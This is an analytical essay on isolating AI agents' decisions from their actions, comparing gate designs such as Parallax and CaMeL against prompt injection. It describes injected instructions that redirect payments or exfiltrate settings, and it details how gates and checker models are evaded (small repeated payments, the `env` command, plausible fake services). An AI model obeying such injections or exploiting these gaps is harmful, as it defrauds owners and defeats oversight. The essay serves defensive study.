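# Separating AI reasoning from execution: what it secures and what it does not

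## What it means to separate reasoning from execution

Separating reasoning from execution means building an AI system so that one component chooses an action, another carries it out, and a check between them can allow the action, block it or pass it to a person. The approach applies mainly to agents, in which an AI model chooses actions, such as sending an email or running a command, and software carries them out. Operating system designers worked out the underlying principles in the 1970s, and engineers of trading software, insulin pumps and industrial plants separated decisions from actions long before AI agents existed.

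In TechTarget's *Why AI systems need a boundary between reasoning and execution*, Varun Raj, an engineering executive who works on cloud and AI platforms, argues that companies need this boundary. When a model's output triggers an action directly, people can see what happened in the logs afterwards but have no chance to stop it. A boundary gives them that chance and a record of what the model proposed. Raj also concedes that a model can understand a request, choose a permitted tool and take a valid action, yet still produce the wrong outcome for the business. The boundary's value depends largely on how often that happens.

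### An assistant that can pay

Take an assistant that reads its owner's email and can send money from the owner's account. The model at its centre only turns text into more text. Software around the model turns that text into actions, in a loop:

1. The owner asks the assistant to pay this morning's electricity bill. The software hands the model this request, the developer's standing instructions and a list of available tools.
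2. The model produces a tool call, a structured request for one action with its arguments: read email number 4127.
3. The executor, the component that holds the mailbox password and the bank credentials, runs the call.
4. The software adds the result, here the body of the email, to the model's text. The model then produces its next call: send 82 dollars to the power company.

The loop runs until the model writes a final reply instead of a call. *Trustworthy Agentic AI* (Syed, Ahmed and colleagues, 2026) also includes in its definition of such systems that people check on the agent far less often than it acts.

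The weak point is the email body. Anyone who knows the owner's address can send an email, so an outsider can supply part of the text the model uses to choose its next action. Prompt injection exploits this with text, often hidden in a document or web page, that the model follows as an instruction when it should only read it as information. *NOMOS* (2026), which describes a system for checking tool calls, gives an example from a standard test suite. The user asks the agent to pay a bill stored in a file. The file contains a message, written as if it came from the user, that tells the agent to send money to a certain bank account first. If the model complies, it produces a payment call with the same form as a legitimate one, and an executor that doesn't check calls will make the payment.

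Criminals have started to try this. *Prompt Injection Goes After the Inbox* (Trent, 2026) describes a campaign that the firm Sublime Security observed on 22 October 2026. The emails carried fake invoices for around $88,000 and went mostly to financial controllers. A person who opened one saw ordinary invoice fraud, but the message also contained an instruction for any AI agent that processed it. The instruction was in white text one pixel high, encoded in characters that do not show on a screen.

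### Why a rule in the prompt does not hold

The simplest remedy is to tell the model in its standing instructions never to pay an account that the owner has not approved. But the model receives both this instruction and the email as text. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a 2025 article by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, compares this with an older attack in which people typed database commands into web forms. Developers fixed that by marking the form's contents as data, which the database engine then never executes. A language model has no equivalent marking. It predicts the next token, a word or piece of a word, from all the text before it. Training can make it more likely to follow the developer's instruction than the email's, but cannot guarantee that it will.

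Several groups have measured those odds. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports a public contest in which 464 people made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models. To win, an attack had to trigger a specified harmful action and leave no trace in the agent's final reply to its user. Attacks succeeded against every model, at rates from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. The contestants could see the conversation and knew which tool call they were aiming for, so real attackers would probably do worse on a single try, but they can try again. VentureBeat reported Anthropic's figures for attacks on Claude Opus 4.6, another older model, working through a graphical interface without safeguards. The success rate was 17.8% for one attempt and 78.6% by the 200th.

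Newer models resist attacks much better. According to The Decoder, Anthropic reported no successful attacks on Claude Opus 5 in 129 browser scenarios, and a 2.0% attack success rate after 15 attempts in a more general test. But results vary widely between models. In *Agent Money Benchmark* (2026), a test of how agents spend, GPT-6 Astra passed all 26 adversarial tasks, while GPT-6 Luna, from the same family, passed two. A developer who chooses well gets a strong filter, but how often it fails still depends on the model, the setting and how persistent the attacker is.

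*APort Vault* (2026) describes two ways to stop a transfer. Either the model declines to request it, or something between the model and the tool blocks it. *Proof-Gated Signing* (2026) reports both outcomes in a small trial where two models operated a cryptocurrency wallet and six of the ten tasks contained an injection. Most of the injections failed because the models ignored or declined them. One injection, placed in documentation, directed deposits to a fake service for moving tokens between blockchains. Both models proposed the deposit, and the check on their requests blocked it.

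### Three designs that share a name

Engineers use "separation" for at least three different designs. In the simplest, the model can only propose tool calls. A gate checks each call and allows, blocks or escalates it, and only the executor behind the gate holds any permissions. An agent design called Parallax works this way. *Agenra* (2026) presents a language for writing a gate's rules and aims for the gate to block forbidden calls even when the agent makes them deliberately. Such a gate would forbid the same calls whether or not an email had fooled the model.

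A gate acts after a manipulated model has already produced a call. Another design keeps the manipulation away from the planning. One model reads only the owner's request and writes the plan: open the bill, extract the amount and account number, and pay. A second model, which has no tools, reads the email and fills in the values. CaMeL, a system from 2025, builds on this dual-model pattern. The pattern secures control flow (which actions run, in what order and under what conditions), so a sentence hidden in the email cannot add a second payment. It does not by itself secure data flow, meaning which values reach which actions. The account number still comes from the email, so a forged bill can send the planned payment to the wrong account unless something also restricts where that number may come from.

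A sandbox limits running code to certain files or network addresses. Many agents need one because they write and run programs instead of making simple calls such as "send 82 dollars". *Tether* (2026) deals with agents that work in a terminal, where the wording of a command often does not reveal its effects. Its monitor runs the command against a protected layer over the real files and uses the program's requests to the operating system to infer what the program read, copied or uploaded. *Kairos* (2026) gives a related reason for guarding the edge of the sandbox, which is that a gate on tool calls covers only the actions that an agent declares. For the email assistant, a sandbox could block access to the owner's tax files. It could not stop a bad payment by itself, because the assistant needs access to the bank to make legitimate payments.

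### Where the ideas come from

Two of the principles behind this separation appear in *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* (Saltzer and Schroeder, 1975). Least privilege means that every program runs with only the permissions its job requires. An assistant that only summarises mail should therefore have no payment tool, which protects the account better than any rule about payments. Complete mediation means that the system checks the authority for every access to every object. Saltzer and Schroeder were wary of shortcuts such as storing the result of a check. If a gate stores its approval of a payee, it will keep allowing payments after the owner withdraws the approval, unless the stored result is updated too. The paper also lists open design, the principle that protection should not depend on attackers' ignorance of the mechanism.

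Three years earlier, Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, a report for the US Air Force, had described the component that does the checking. Anderson called the idea a reference monitor and set three requirements for any mechanism that implements it:

- Nobody can tamper with it.
- The system always invokes it.
- It is small enough for people to analyse and test completely.

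Anderson showed what the requirements exclude by applying them to GCOS III, an operating system of the time. The hardware confined each user's program to its own memory, but suspended that check while the operating system worked on the program's behalf, so the check did not always run. The operating system itself did not qualify as the monitor either, because it and its supporting software contained between 200,000 and 300,000 instructions, far too many to verify.

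Anderson concluded that any program not subject to the check becomes part of the security apparatus and has to meet the same standards. That apparatus is now called the trusted computing base, the components that must work correctly for the security claim to hold. In the email assistant, it contains the gate, the executor, the written policy, the list of approved payees and the connections between them. Keeping the model outside it is the main benefit of a gate, since nobody can verify a large language model in Anderson's sense. According to *Tether*, many production systems use a second language model to review proposed commands, which loses this benefit by putting a model back among the trusted components. When *Proof-Gated Signing* tested two such reviewers on a scripted version of the fake deposit, both allowed it. Trusted components other than models can also fail. In an example from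 *Agenra*, an address directory is compromised, so the gate follows its lookup rule correctly but approves the wrong address.

OpenSSH, a widely used program for logging in to remote computers, is a working example of this division. Provos, Friedl and Honeyman (2003), in *Preventing Privilege Escalation*, applied privilege separation to it, splitting the program so that the part exposed to attackers lacks the permissions that could do damage. An unprivileged process handles all network traffic. When it needs a privileged operation, it sends a request to a small monitor process, which checks that the request is valid at that stage of the login, performs the operation and returns the result. The exposed process can obtain a digital signature, for instance, but never receives the signing key. Provos and colleagues assumed that an attacker might gain complete control of the exposed process. After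 the split, several past bugs that had given attackers control of the whole machine would no longer have done so. About a third of the code, counting third-party libraries, still ran with privilege. OpenSSH has since made privilege separation mandatory.

The model in an agent occupies the place of that exposed process, but the comparison makes the agent look more secure than it is. Many of the questions the monitor decides in OpenSSH have exact answers, such as whether a password matches, but whether the owner really owes somebody 499 dollars can't be checked in the same way.

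Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* (1988) describes the resulting problem with a story from Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time. A compiler had permission to write to the directory that held its usage statistics and the company's billing records. It also wrote debugging output to any file a user named. When one user named the billing file, the operating system confirmed that the compiler could write there, and the debugging output replaced the billing records. The permission check worked correctly, but the compiler held authority from both its user and its own licence and could not indicate which one it was using. Hardy's remedy was the capability, a token that both identifies a file and grants the right to write to it, so that users can hand over only access they already have.

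An assistant with its owner's bank credentials and a stranger's email is in the compiler's position. If the gate checks only whether the assistant may make payments, it will allow a payment that the stranger requested. David C calls language models "inherently confusable" deputies and cites a rule of thumb from Simon Willison and Baibhav Bista that a model's privileges should drop to those of any party whose text it processes. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026) models a gate of this kind as a set C of tools that the agent may use. When the agent reads untrusted text, the gate removes a fixed group of tools from C. The email assistant would lose its payment tool when it opened a stranger's message, so it could not pay a genuine bill that arrived by email, which is most of what its owner wanted it to do.

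### What a working gate guarantees

Let P be the set of actions that the policy permits and E the set that the executor carries out. If the gate meets Anderson's requirements and applies its policy correctly, then

E ⊆ P

that is, every executed action is a permitted one. Now let H be the set of harmful actions. The guarantee places the harm that occurs, E ∩ H, inside P ∩ H, and it rules out harm altogether only if P ∩ H is empty. Actions in P ∩ H do permitted harm: damage done by an action that the gate is right, under its rules, to allow.

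Suppose the email assistant's only policy rule is that no payment may exceed 500 dollars. An attacker hides an instruction in an email to pay 5,000 dollars, and the gate blocks the payment. The attacker then sends another email requesting 499 dollars. That payment is in P, so the gate correctly allows it. Ten such emails would cost the owner 4,990 dollars, because the rule applies to each payment separately. A gate that capped total payments at 500 dollars a day would limit the loss to that amount each day.

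Even a crude rule, such as a fixed spending limit, is useful. *Holding Agents Accountable with Verifiable Agent Insurance* (2026) describes how an agent called Lobstar Wilde sent a stranger tokens worth about 450,000 dollars, by its operator's estimate, when the stranger had asked for about 320 dollars' worth. A limit of 500 dollars would have blocked the transfer without anyone needing to establish what the agent was trying to do.

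*Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (2026) gives a way to find harm that injection causes and the gate permits, without first defining harm. It compares the real agent with a reference agent that follows its plan whatever the untrusted text contains, with both running behind the same gate. When a design is insecure, the reason is usually a call that the gate allows but the reference agent could never make, such as the 499-dollar payment to the attacker.

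The obvious response is to shrink P. In *NOMOS*, the gate allows a transfer only if the user has named the recipient or the recipient appears in the account's history. This blocks the attacker's transfer of 499 dollars as well as the one for 5,000. It also blocks a transfer of zero dollars whose subject line carries the user's financial data to an unknown account. The same transfer to a payee already in the history goes through, because the gate does not inspect the subject line. The rule also produces false positives, which are legitimate actions that the gate blocks. For example, if the user asks the assistant to pay a first bill from a new electrician without giving the electrician's name, the gate blocks the payment.

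Adding rules helps only where the gate has a fact to check. In *Agent Money Benchmark*, 112 of 141 recorded scam events were repeat charges or prices above the listed one, which a gate with the receipts and the price list could catch. But the gate may have no way to look up anything that distinguishes the electrician's bill from a good forgery, in which case it has to allow both or block both. *Kairos* describes the same problem for any monitor that can only allow or block an action, and its own design can also hold an action and release it later. Holding a payment leaves time to ask the owner, who knows whether the electrician came.

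## Parallax: a model that can only propose actions

*Parallax* (Fokou, 2026), published in April, describes an agent in which the model cannot carry out actions itself. The agent runs as two separate programs. The first communicates with the model, cannot access files or run commands, and may connect only to the model's provider and to the second program, the engine. The engine has full access to the computer and contains both the gate and the executor. The model can affect the outside world only by sending the engine a tool call. This design comes from OpenSSH, and Fokou likewise assumes that an attacker may take full control of the exposed program.

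Fokou also released OpenParallax, an open-source personal assistant that follows the design. Its documentation covers the rules, settings and 13 test runs, and in several places describes weaker protection than the paper does.

### One request through the gate

Suppose the owner asks the assistant why a program cannot connect to its database. The assistant reads a web page about the error, and the page contains a hidden instruction to send the program's settings to a "validation service". The model complies and proposes a web request that would send them there.

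The engine first runs checks compiled into its code, which protect its own configuration and logs. This request touches neither. Up to four further checks follow:

1. **Fixed rules.** A policy file lists actions to deny, actions to allow and actions to pass to a later check. It denies any attempt to read the owner's login keys, for example. An action that matches no rule goes to the classifiers.
2. **Classifiers.** A set of text patterns looks for known forms of attack, such as a command that downloads a script and immediately runs it. Alongside it, DeBERTa, a small language model that Fokou trained on about 16,000 examples, estimates whether the call looks like prompt injection. Either can block the call. If DeBERTa suspects an injection but is less than 85% confident, the call goes to the second model.
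3. **A second model.** A separate large language model (Claude Haiku 4.5 in the tests) reads the call and answers "allow", "block" or "escalate".
4. **A person.** The owner sees the tool, its arguments and the gate's reasons. If nobody answers within five minutes, the gate blocks the call.

Few calls go through all four checks. The code on OpenParallax's *Defense in Depth* page lets a call through as soon as one check allows it, unless a rule requires a later one, although the same page states that an attacker has to defeat every check at once. Under the default policy, the web request to the validation service goes from the fixed rules straight to the second model, skipping DeBERTa and all but two of the text patterns. Emails, chat messages, file writes and deletions take the same route.

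One language model usually decides whether to allow these actions, so the gate guarantees less for them. An owner can read the policy file and know that the assistant will not open the login keys, but whether it will post settings to a stranger depends on how a model answers. The set of permitted actions, P, has a definite boundary where fixed rules decide, and elsewhere the owner can rely only on the model's success rate.

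Some commands skip all four checks. According to OpenParallax's *Changelog*, the gate has a list of common developer commands, including `git`, `npm` and `make`, that it allows immediately when they stand alone on a line.

Fokou also makes the model load tools in groups as it needs them, reasoning that a compromised model cannot misuse a tool it has not loaded. But the untrusted program handles the loading without a check by the gate, so a compromised model can load any tool. The restriction is firmer for helper agents that the main agent starts, because the engine gives each one a fixed set of tools and no way to request more.

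### A checker that knows nothing about the task

The second model receives the type of action and its contents, but not the conversation or the owner's request, and it has no tools. The hidden instruction that fooled the first model therefore reaches the second only if the attacker also places it inside the tool call.

An attacker might manage that, since a call can contain a whole email or file. The second model's instructions are to treat the call as data, but language models can fail to follow such instructions. Fokou adds a random token to the instructions as a tripwire, and the model must repeat it in its answer. If text in the call makes the model abandon its instructions, the token will probably be missing, and the gate blocks the action. The token does not help if the model keeps to the required format but accepts a false statement in the call, for example that the address belongs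 to the company's own test server.

The software also has a small flaw in how it reads the answer. According to OpenParallax's *Tier 2*, if the token is present but the verdict is a word the software does not recognise, the gate treats it as "allow". This is an exception to the claim in *Parallax* that every check blocks when something goes wrong.

Keeping the second model ignorant makes it harder to manipulate and worse at judging ambiguous actions. Sending settings to a validation service is reasonable if the owner uses that service, and the second model has no way to find out. Its errors in the tests were of this kind. Three attacks got past the gate in its default setting, all because the second model allowed them:

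- It judged the deletion of a file in the temporary folder to be low-risk.
- It accepted a web request to a plausible-looking validation address.
- It classed the command `env` as a harmless read. The command prints a program's environment variables, which often include passwords and access keys.

It also blocked four legitimate commands in the run with the strictest setting because it could not determine their purpose. Showing it the conversation would help with such cases but would also expose it to the text that had compromised the first model. Showing it only the owner's original request might be a workable middle ground, because the attacker did not write that request.

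### Labels and rollback

The gate checks each call separately, without a record of previous ones. This protects it from an attacker who wears the model down over a long conversation, but it can miss harm that builds up over several steps, like the ten payments of 499 dollars in the earlier example. Stealing a password may take three calls that each look harmless: one to read a file, one to write its contents into a web address, and one to open that address.

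Parallax uses information-flow control against such sequences. The engine labels sensitive data when reading it and refuses to send that data out of the machine. In OpenParallax's *Information Flow Control*, the labels depend on a file's name and location. A file called `patient-intake-2024.pdf` gets a high label because its name contains "patient". The same document named `scan-12.pdf` would count as public unless the owner had written a rule covering it. Fokou acknowledges that sensitive data goes unlabelled when no rule matches it. The label policy also allows any type of action it does not list, including those of newly added outside tools.

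Another difficulty is that the model may rephrase the data, so the engine can't trace which words of an outgoing email came from which file. In the first release of OpenParallax, an agent could read `.env`, a file that typically holds passwords, and then send an email, which is very close to the theft that Fokou uses to explain why labels are necessary. Version 0.1.1 fixed this by recording the highest label seen in a session and applying it to whatever the agent sends afterwards. The fix would also stop an unrelated email to a colleague.

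Rollback deals with damage that the gate fails to prevent. Before an action overwrites, deletes or moves a file, the engine saves a copy that the owner can restore. OpenParallax's *Chronicle* does this only for the assistant's three file tools. The engine saves nothing if the assistant deletes a file with a typed command or changes a database, although *Parallax* lists database writes among the actions that rollback covers. The engine keeps up to 100 copies for 30 days, so a compromised model could make a damaging edit and then a hundred trivial ones to displace the copy needed to undo it, provided the gate let them all through.

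Restoring a saved copy cannot undo a sent email or a leaked password. Fokou recommends that the fixed rules require a person's approval for these irreversible actions, but the default policy sends them to the second model.

### Testing the gate without the model

Fokou first tested the complete system with Claude Sonnet 4.6, Claude Haiku 4.5 and Llama 3.1 8B under three conditions: no protection, safety instructions in the prompt, and the full gate. All three models refused every attack in every condition. As OpenParallax's *Methodology* explains, the gate never had to act, so the comparison revealed nothing about it. The result also suggests that the attacks were easy to spot, because contestants in the public competition described earlier broke all 13 models they attacked. When Fokou briefly tried Qwen 2.5 3B, a small model with less safety training, it readily proposed deleting files.

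The main test, which Fokou calls Assume-Compromise Evaluation, therefore leaves the model out. A test program submits harmful tool calls directly to the gate, as if an attacker already controlled the model completely. This suits a gate, which is meant to block harmful calls even when the model has failed. A real attacker would be more demanding in one respect, because they could study each refusal and adapt rather than submit calls from a prepared list, as the test program does.

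The list contained 280 attacks in nine categories, including disguised commands, chains of tool calls and attempts to tamper with the gate. To count false positives, Fokou also submitted 50 legitimate actions, such as installing software packages and sending email.

| Setting | Attacks blocked | Legitimate actions blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Default | 277 of 280 (98.9%) | 0 of 50 |
| Strictest | 280 of 280 | 18 of 50 (36%) |

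The settings differ in how many types of action DeBERTa checks. The strictest setting has it check all of them, while the default skips seven: writing, deleting, moving and copying files, sending emails and chat messages, and making web requests. DeBERTa was trained to detect injection using text examples that included no tool calls, and it misclassified ordinary emails and file contents as attacks. It caused 14 of the 18 false positives, each with a confidence of 1.00. Fokou expects that training it on real tool calls would let it check more of them without blocking legitimate work.

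OpenParallax's *Tier 1* presents the default as a good tradeoff because it lowers detection by 1.1 percentage points and false positives by 36. That seems right for a personal assistant. Fokou points out that people switch off security tools that keep interrupting them, and they would probably turn off a gate within a week if it blocked a third of legitimate actions. A company whose agent can reach customer records might reasonably accept more false positives in exchange for better detection, at least for the few actions that could expose those records.

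Dropping DeBERTa altogether turned out much worse. In a run described in OpenParallax's *Reports*, the text patterns took its place, and the gate missed between 92% and 100% of attacks in three categories where it had previously missed none. Fokou reversed the change, but DeBERTa still does not come with the program. If an owner never downloads it, the gate runs without it and the owner gets a single warning at the start of the session.

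### How much the figures prove

Fokou developed the rules and measured their success on largely the same attacks. OpenParallax's *Run History* records that in the first run that submitted calls directly, the gate missed 19.2% of the attacks aimed at the gate itself. Fokou then added 17 new text patterns and rules for the credential files and system folders that had been left open, and ran the test again. A later rule that allowed all writes to the assistant's own folder let more attacks through in four categories and was removed. As the settings changed from run to run, the false-positive rate went from 34% to 66%, then to 40%, 36% and finally zero.

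Fokou calls this the normal life of a security policy, and administrators do refine firewalls the same way. But a score on attacks that shaped the rules mostly shows that the rules fit those attacks. A fairer test would use held-out attacks, which nobody tries on the gate until the rules are final, but Fokou reports no such test. The zero false positives have the same weakness, because Fokou adjusted the settings until the 50 legitimate actions passed.

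The count also leaves out some legitimate actions that the gate apparently blocked. To test the human check, Fokou wrote 12 deliberately ambiguous cases, such as overwriting the history of a shared code project. Four reached the human check, where the test program answered in place of a person. Earlier automatic checks caught the other eight, which Fokou describes as correct behaviour. But seven of the 12 were legitimate, so the automatic checks seem to have stopped at least three actions that the owner would have approved.

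*Parallax* reports that fixed rules and classifiers dealt with 73.6% of the attacks, and takes this as a sign that the gate depends little on the second model. But according to the project's own *Reports*, that breakdown comes from a run with the strictest setting. By default, seven types of action skip DeBERTa, so the second model probably decides a much larger share.

The sample of legitimate actions is small, too. If the gate wrongly blocked 5.8% of them, it would still get through 50 without a mistake about one time in 20:

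(1 − 0.058)^50 ≈ 0.05

The result is therefore compatible with an actual false-positive rate of about 6%. At that rate, an assistant that made 100 legitimate calls a day would have about six blocked. This estimate assumes that the owner's work resembles the 50 test actions, which came mainly from software development.

For the attacks, the important question is what happens over many attempts. The gate missed 3 of 280, or 1.1%. If every attempt had that chance of success, independently of the others, the probability of at least one success in k attempts would be

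1 − (1 − 3/280)^k

This gives 10% after 10 attempts, 50% after 65 and 66% after 100. The default settings allow the second model 100 evaluations a day and then, until midnight, block every action that needs one. This limits how many times a compromised model can try to get past the second model, but it also gives it an easy way to stop its owner's emails for the rest of the day by using up the evaluations.

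The formula shows how quickly a small miss rate can add up, but it does not predict what a real attacker would achieve. Attempts are not independent. A fixed rule that denies access to a file will still deny it on the hundredth attempt, while `env` would probably work every time. The 280 attacks are also not a random sample of what attackers try. An attacker looks for calls that work, and the gate gives some help with this. When it blocks a call, it returns the reason, including which protected path the call matched, so that an honest model will not waste time retrying. But a miss does not always cause serious damage. Deleting a temporary file may do no harm, and an outsider cannot use the passwords that `env` prints until they leave the machine.

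### Scripts, the sandbox and the engine

The gate inspects the command that starts a script, but not the script itself. If a compromised model writes a harmful program to a file and then runs it, the gate receives one file write and one ordinary-looking command. Fokou lists this as a limitation and proposes tracking which files the agent has written. By default, only the second model checks the contents of a new file, since DeBERTa skips file writes and the text patterns cover only fields such as the file's path. The list of exempt commands makes this problem worse, because `make` and `npm` run instructions stored in project files. If the second model misses a harmful line in one of those files, the gate may not be able to stop it later.

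A sandbox is supposed to confine the untrusted program. *Parallax* describes a startup test that tries forbidden operations and stops the system from running if any succeeds. According to OpenParallax's *Process Isolation*, however, the agent starts even if the operating system offers no suitable sandbox, because the software would otherwise be unusable on many machines. On Windows, the sandbox restricts neither files nor network connections. In April 2026, OpenParallax's *Linux* listed network restriction on Linux as planned, but by June OpenParallax's *Structural Isolation* included it for recent versions.

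To exploit a missing sandbox, an attacker has to find a bug in the program around the model and run their own code inside that program. Fooling the model is not enough, because the program still turns the model's output into tool calls. On a system that doesn't restrict network access, the attacker's code could read the assistant's files and send them anywhere without passing through the gate.

Fokou calls the engine the sole trusted component and accepts that the entire design fails if an attacker compromises it, for instance through a tampered update. Any gate has a trusted computing base, but this one is large because the engine contains the gate, the code for 67 actions, a web server and connections to seven messaging services. It is hard to see how anyone could analyse and test it completely, as Anderson required.

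Parallax also differs from OpenSSH, which keeps network traffic in its unprivileged process. Parallax denies the untrusted program general network access, so the privileged engine has to fetch web pages and emails before the model can read them. An attacker's email therefore passes through the engine first, where a bug in the mail code could be disastrous. Moving that code into a third process, with access to the network and little else, would bring the design closer to OpenSSH's.

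### The insurance argument

Fokou argues that the gate is worth having even if current models refuse every attack in the test without it. Those refusals come from safety training, which attackers keep trying to defeat, and an owner may switch to a model with less of that training. If the model fails, safety instructions in its prompt fail too, but a gate in a separate process keeps working.

This is a good argument for the fixed rules, which give the same result whatever has happened to the model. The argument is weaker for emails, web requests and file writes, which are protected largely by another language model whose caution also comes from training. The second model is isolated, so one attack is less likely to defeat both, but how much less likely is unknown because Fokou's test did not include an attacker who adapted each call to the second model's answers.

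The checks add a moderate delay. A typical call that reaches the classifiers or the second model waits about two seconds, while the fixed rules take less than a millisecond. An owner who wants firmer protection can write rules that deny whole classes of irreversible action or require approval for them, but this causes more interruptions.

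## CaMeL: a planner that never reads untrusted text

The gate in Parallax acts after a model has read the attacker's email and proposed an action. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, 2025) describes CaMeL, which keeps the email away from the model that chooses the actions. That model writes its whole plan as a program before the software opens any email. An interpreter then runs the program, records where each value came from and checks that record before every tool call.

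### Two models and a controller

CaMeL develops an idea that Willison (2023) proposed for email assistants in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*. Willison's privileged model plans from the owner's request, while a quarantined model with no tools reads untrusted text. The controller, which is ordinary software, runs the tools and carries values between the two models.

The controller sends variable names instead of text to the privileged model. If the owner asks for a summary of the latest email, the privileged model requests the email, and the controller stores it as `$VAR1`. The privileged model then requests a summary of `$VAR1`. The controller sends the email to the quarantined model and stores the resulting summary as `$VAR2`. The privileged model then instructs the controller to display `$VAR2`, without having read the email or the summary. The controller may return the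 quarantined model's output to the privileged model only if it can verify that output, for instance when the quarantined model had to choose from a fixed list of categories.

Willison called this solution "pretty bad" because it makes assistants harder to build and less pleasant to use, and a single mistake that lets untrusted text reach the privileged model removes the protection. Debenedetti and colleagues pointed out that it also leaves the data flow unprotected. Willison (2025) says in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that this flaw was new to him. For example, if a user asks the assistant to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in a file of meeting notes, an attacker who can edit the notes can substitute another address.

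### One bill, step by step

Suppose the owner of the email assistant asks it again to pay this morning's electricity bill. In CaMeL the privileged model, or planner, receives that sentence and a description of the tools. It writes a program in a restricted form of Python, which might look like this:

```
email = search_email("electricity bill", date="today")
bill = quarantined_model(
    "Find the account number and the amount due",
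    email, output_format=Bill)
send_money(recipient=bill.account, amount=bill.amount)
```

The interpreter runs the program one line at a time:

1. It searches the mailbox and stores the email with a label. One part of the label lists the value's sources, here a message from outside. The other part lists its permitted readers.
2. It passes the email to the quarantined model, which must return an account number and an amount in a fixed format. Both inherit the email's label because the model derived them from the email.
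3. Before it sends any money, it calls a policy. This is a short Python function that receives the name of the tool, the arguments and their labels, and returns "allow" or "deny".

CaMeL can label individual values because the quarantined model works like a function with known inputs, so the interpreter can give its output the labels of all its inputs. Since Parallax's model may rephrase anything it has read, Parallax has to label the whole session.

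An attacker might try to change the control flow by hiding an instruction in the bill to first pay 499 dollars to another account. The quarantined model may well try to follow it, but it cannot make payments. Its output goes into the variable `bill`, which the planner never reads, so the program still contains a single payment, however persuasive the hidden text is.

An attack on the data flow changes a value the program uses without changing the program itself. The hidden instruction tells the quarantined model to report the attacker's account number as the power company's. The plan then runs as written and pays the wrong account, unless a policy blocks the payment. The label on `bill.account` lists an outside email as its source, so a policy that accepts only recipients named by the owner or already on an approved list will deny the call. Labels also list who may read a value, which lets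 a policy protect secrets. If only the owner and Bob may read the document, a policy can refuse to send it to any other address.

The label does not show whether a value is correct, so CaMeL cannot distinguish the new electrician's bill from a forgery either. In a passage Willison quotes, Debenedetti and colleagues acknowledge that users have to write and maintain these policies, and that frequent requests for approval wear people down until they approve everything.

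CaMeL also depends on the planner's input containing no untrusted text. If the owner pastes an attacker's text into the request, the planner reads it as part of the request. Fokou objects in *Parallax* that the planner can still act. This objection matters most when the request contains an attacker's text, because the policies are then the only check on a plan the attacker helped write.

### Related designs

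Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, place CaMeL at the far end of a range of six patterns. In the most restrictive, the model only picks from a list of ready-made actions and never sees their results. In another, the model fixes a list of tool calls in advance, and CaMeL replaces that list with a program. Willison's pattern isolates the reading of untrusted text, as does a simplified version in which a separate model examines each document. The sixth pattern removes the user's prompt from the model's input once it is no longer needed, in case the prompt contains an attack. Even with a fixed program, an injection can alter the contents of a permitted message. If the user asks the assistant to send today's schedule to the boss, an injection in the calendar cannot change the recipient, but it can rewrite the email.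 Beurer-Kellner and colleagues doubt that a fully general agent can offer reliable guarantees with current language models, and they recommend choosing a pattern to suit each application.

FIDES, which Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025) describe in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, combines the same two models with labels but calls its planner again after every step. This lets it react to results but uses more tokens. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) adapted both systems to agents that operate a screen and measured a token overhead of 1.88 times for CaMeL and 29.6 times for FIDES, relative to an undefended agent. FIDES also has an optional exception for values from a small set, such as yes or no. A choice among n values can carry at most log₂ n bits of an attacker's influence, so a yes-or-no answer carries at most one bit and a choice among eight categories at most three.

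### What the protection costs

AgentDojo, the benchmark most of these systems report results on, simulates an office workspace, a Slack account, a bank and a travel agency. It has 97 user tasks, such as paying a bill stored in a file, and 35 attacker goals, such as sending money to a certain account. The test program plants instructions for an attacker's goal in the data the agent's tools return, then checks whether the agent finished the user's task and whether the attacker's goal was met.

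Debenedetti and colleagues report that CaMeL solved 77% of the tasks, against 84% for an undefended agent. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) report in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* that two attacks still counted as successes. In the first, the user told the agent to make a payment by following instructions in a file, which the attacker had rewritten. Debenedetti and colleagues place this outside their threat model. CaMeL is meant to stop untrusted text from diverting an agent from the user's request, and here the user had asked the agent to follow the text. In the second, the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, including the attacker's, so its answer contained the phrase the benchmark checks for.

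Later reruns found a much larger loss than seven percentage points. *SecureClaw* (2026), which presents a competing system, ran CaMeL through an adapter and recorded no successful attacks in 629 attempts, but CaMeL solved only 29 of the 97 tasks without an attack. SecureClaw itself solved 59. In *CaMeLoT*, a comparison by Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), CaMeL solved 49 of the 97 with Claude Haiku 4.5, a small model. These runs used different models and set-ups, and a competitor's adapter may understate CaMeL's performance. Still, a developer who adopts CaMeL should expect to lose more than seven points, at least with a small planner or strict policies.

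Part of the loss comes from planning before seeing the data. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) tested teams of CaMeL agents on a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks with no policies, so no task could fail because of a policy denial. Success still fell by 21.6 percentage points on average across five models, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest, Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. Most failures occurred because the planner had to commit to a plan before it could see the data. An ordinary agent that finds a file missing can look elsewhere, while a CaMeL planner has to foresee the problem and write a branch for it. The planner also has to know the format of every tool's output in advance, so Peters-Gill and colleagues had to add those formats to the tool descriptions.

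The benchmark is less useful for measuring how much protection CaMeL adds, because newer models can resist its older attacks. On a version of AgentDojo that Peters-Gill and colleagues adapted for teams of agents, 36.1% of the attacks succeeded against GPT-4.1 without any defence, while none of 949 succeeded against GPT-5.5. A determined attacker would try other texts, and CaMeL's advantage is that it protects the plan whichever texts they try.

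### A leak through the branch not taken

That advantage depends on the labels being right. The standard for judging them is noninterference, which means that secret inputs have no effect on what an outsider can observe. Let a program P take a public input x and a secret s, and let P(x, s) be the part of its behaviour that an outsider sees. The program satisfies noninterference if

P(x, s) = P(x, s′) for every x, s and s′.

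The same definition covers tampering if untrusted text takes the place of the secret and the values labelled trusted take the place of the outsider's view. It then requires those values to stay the same no matter what an attacker writes.

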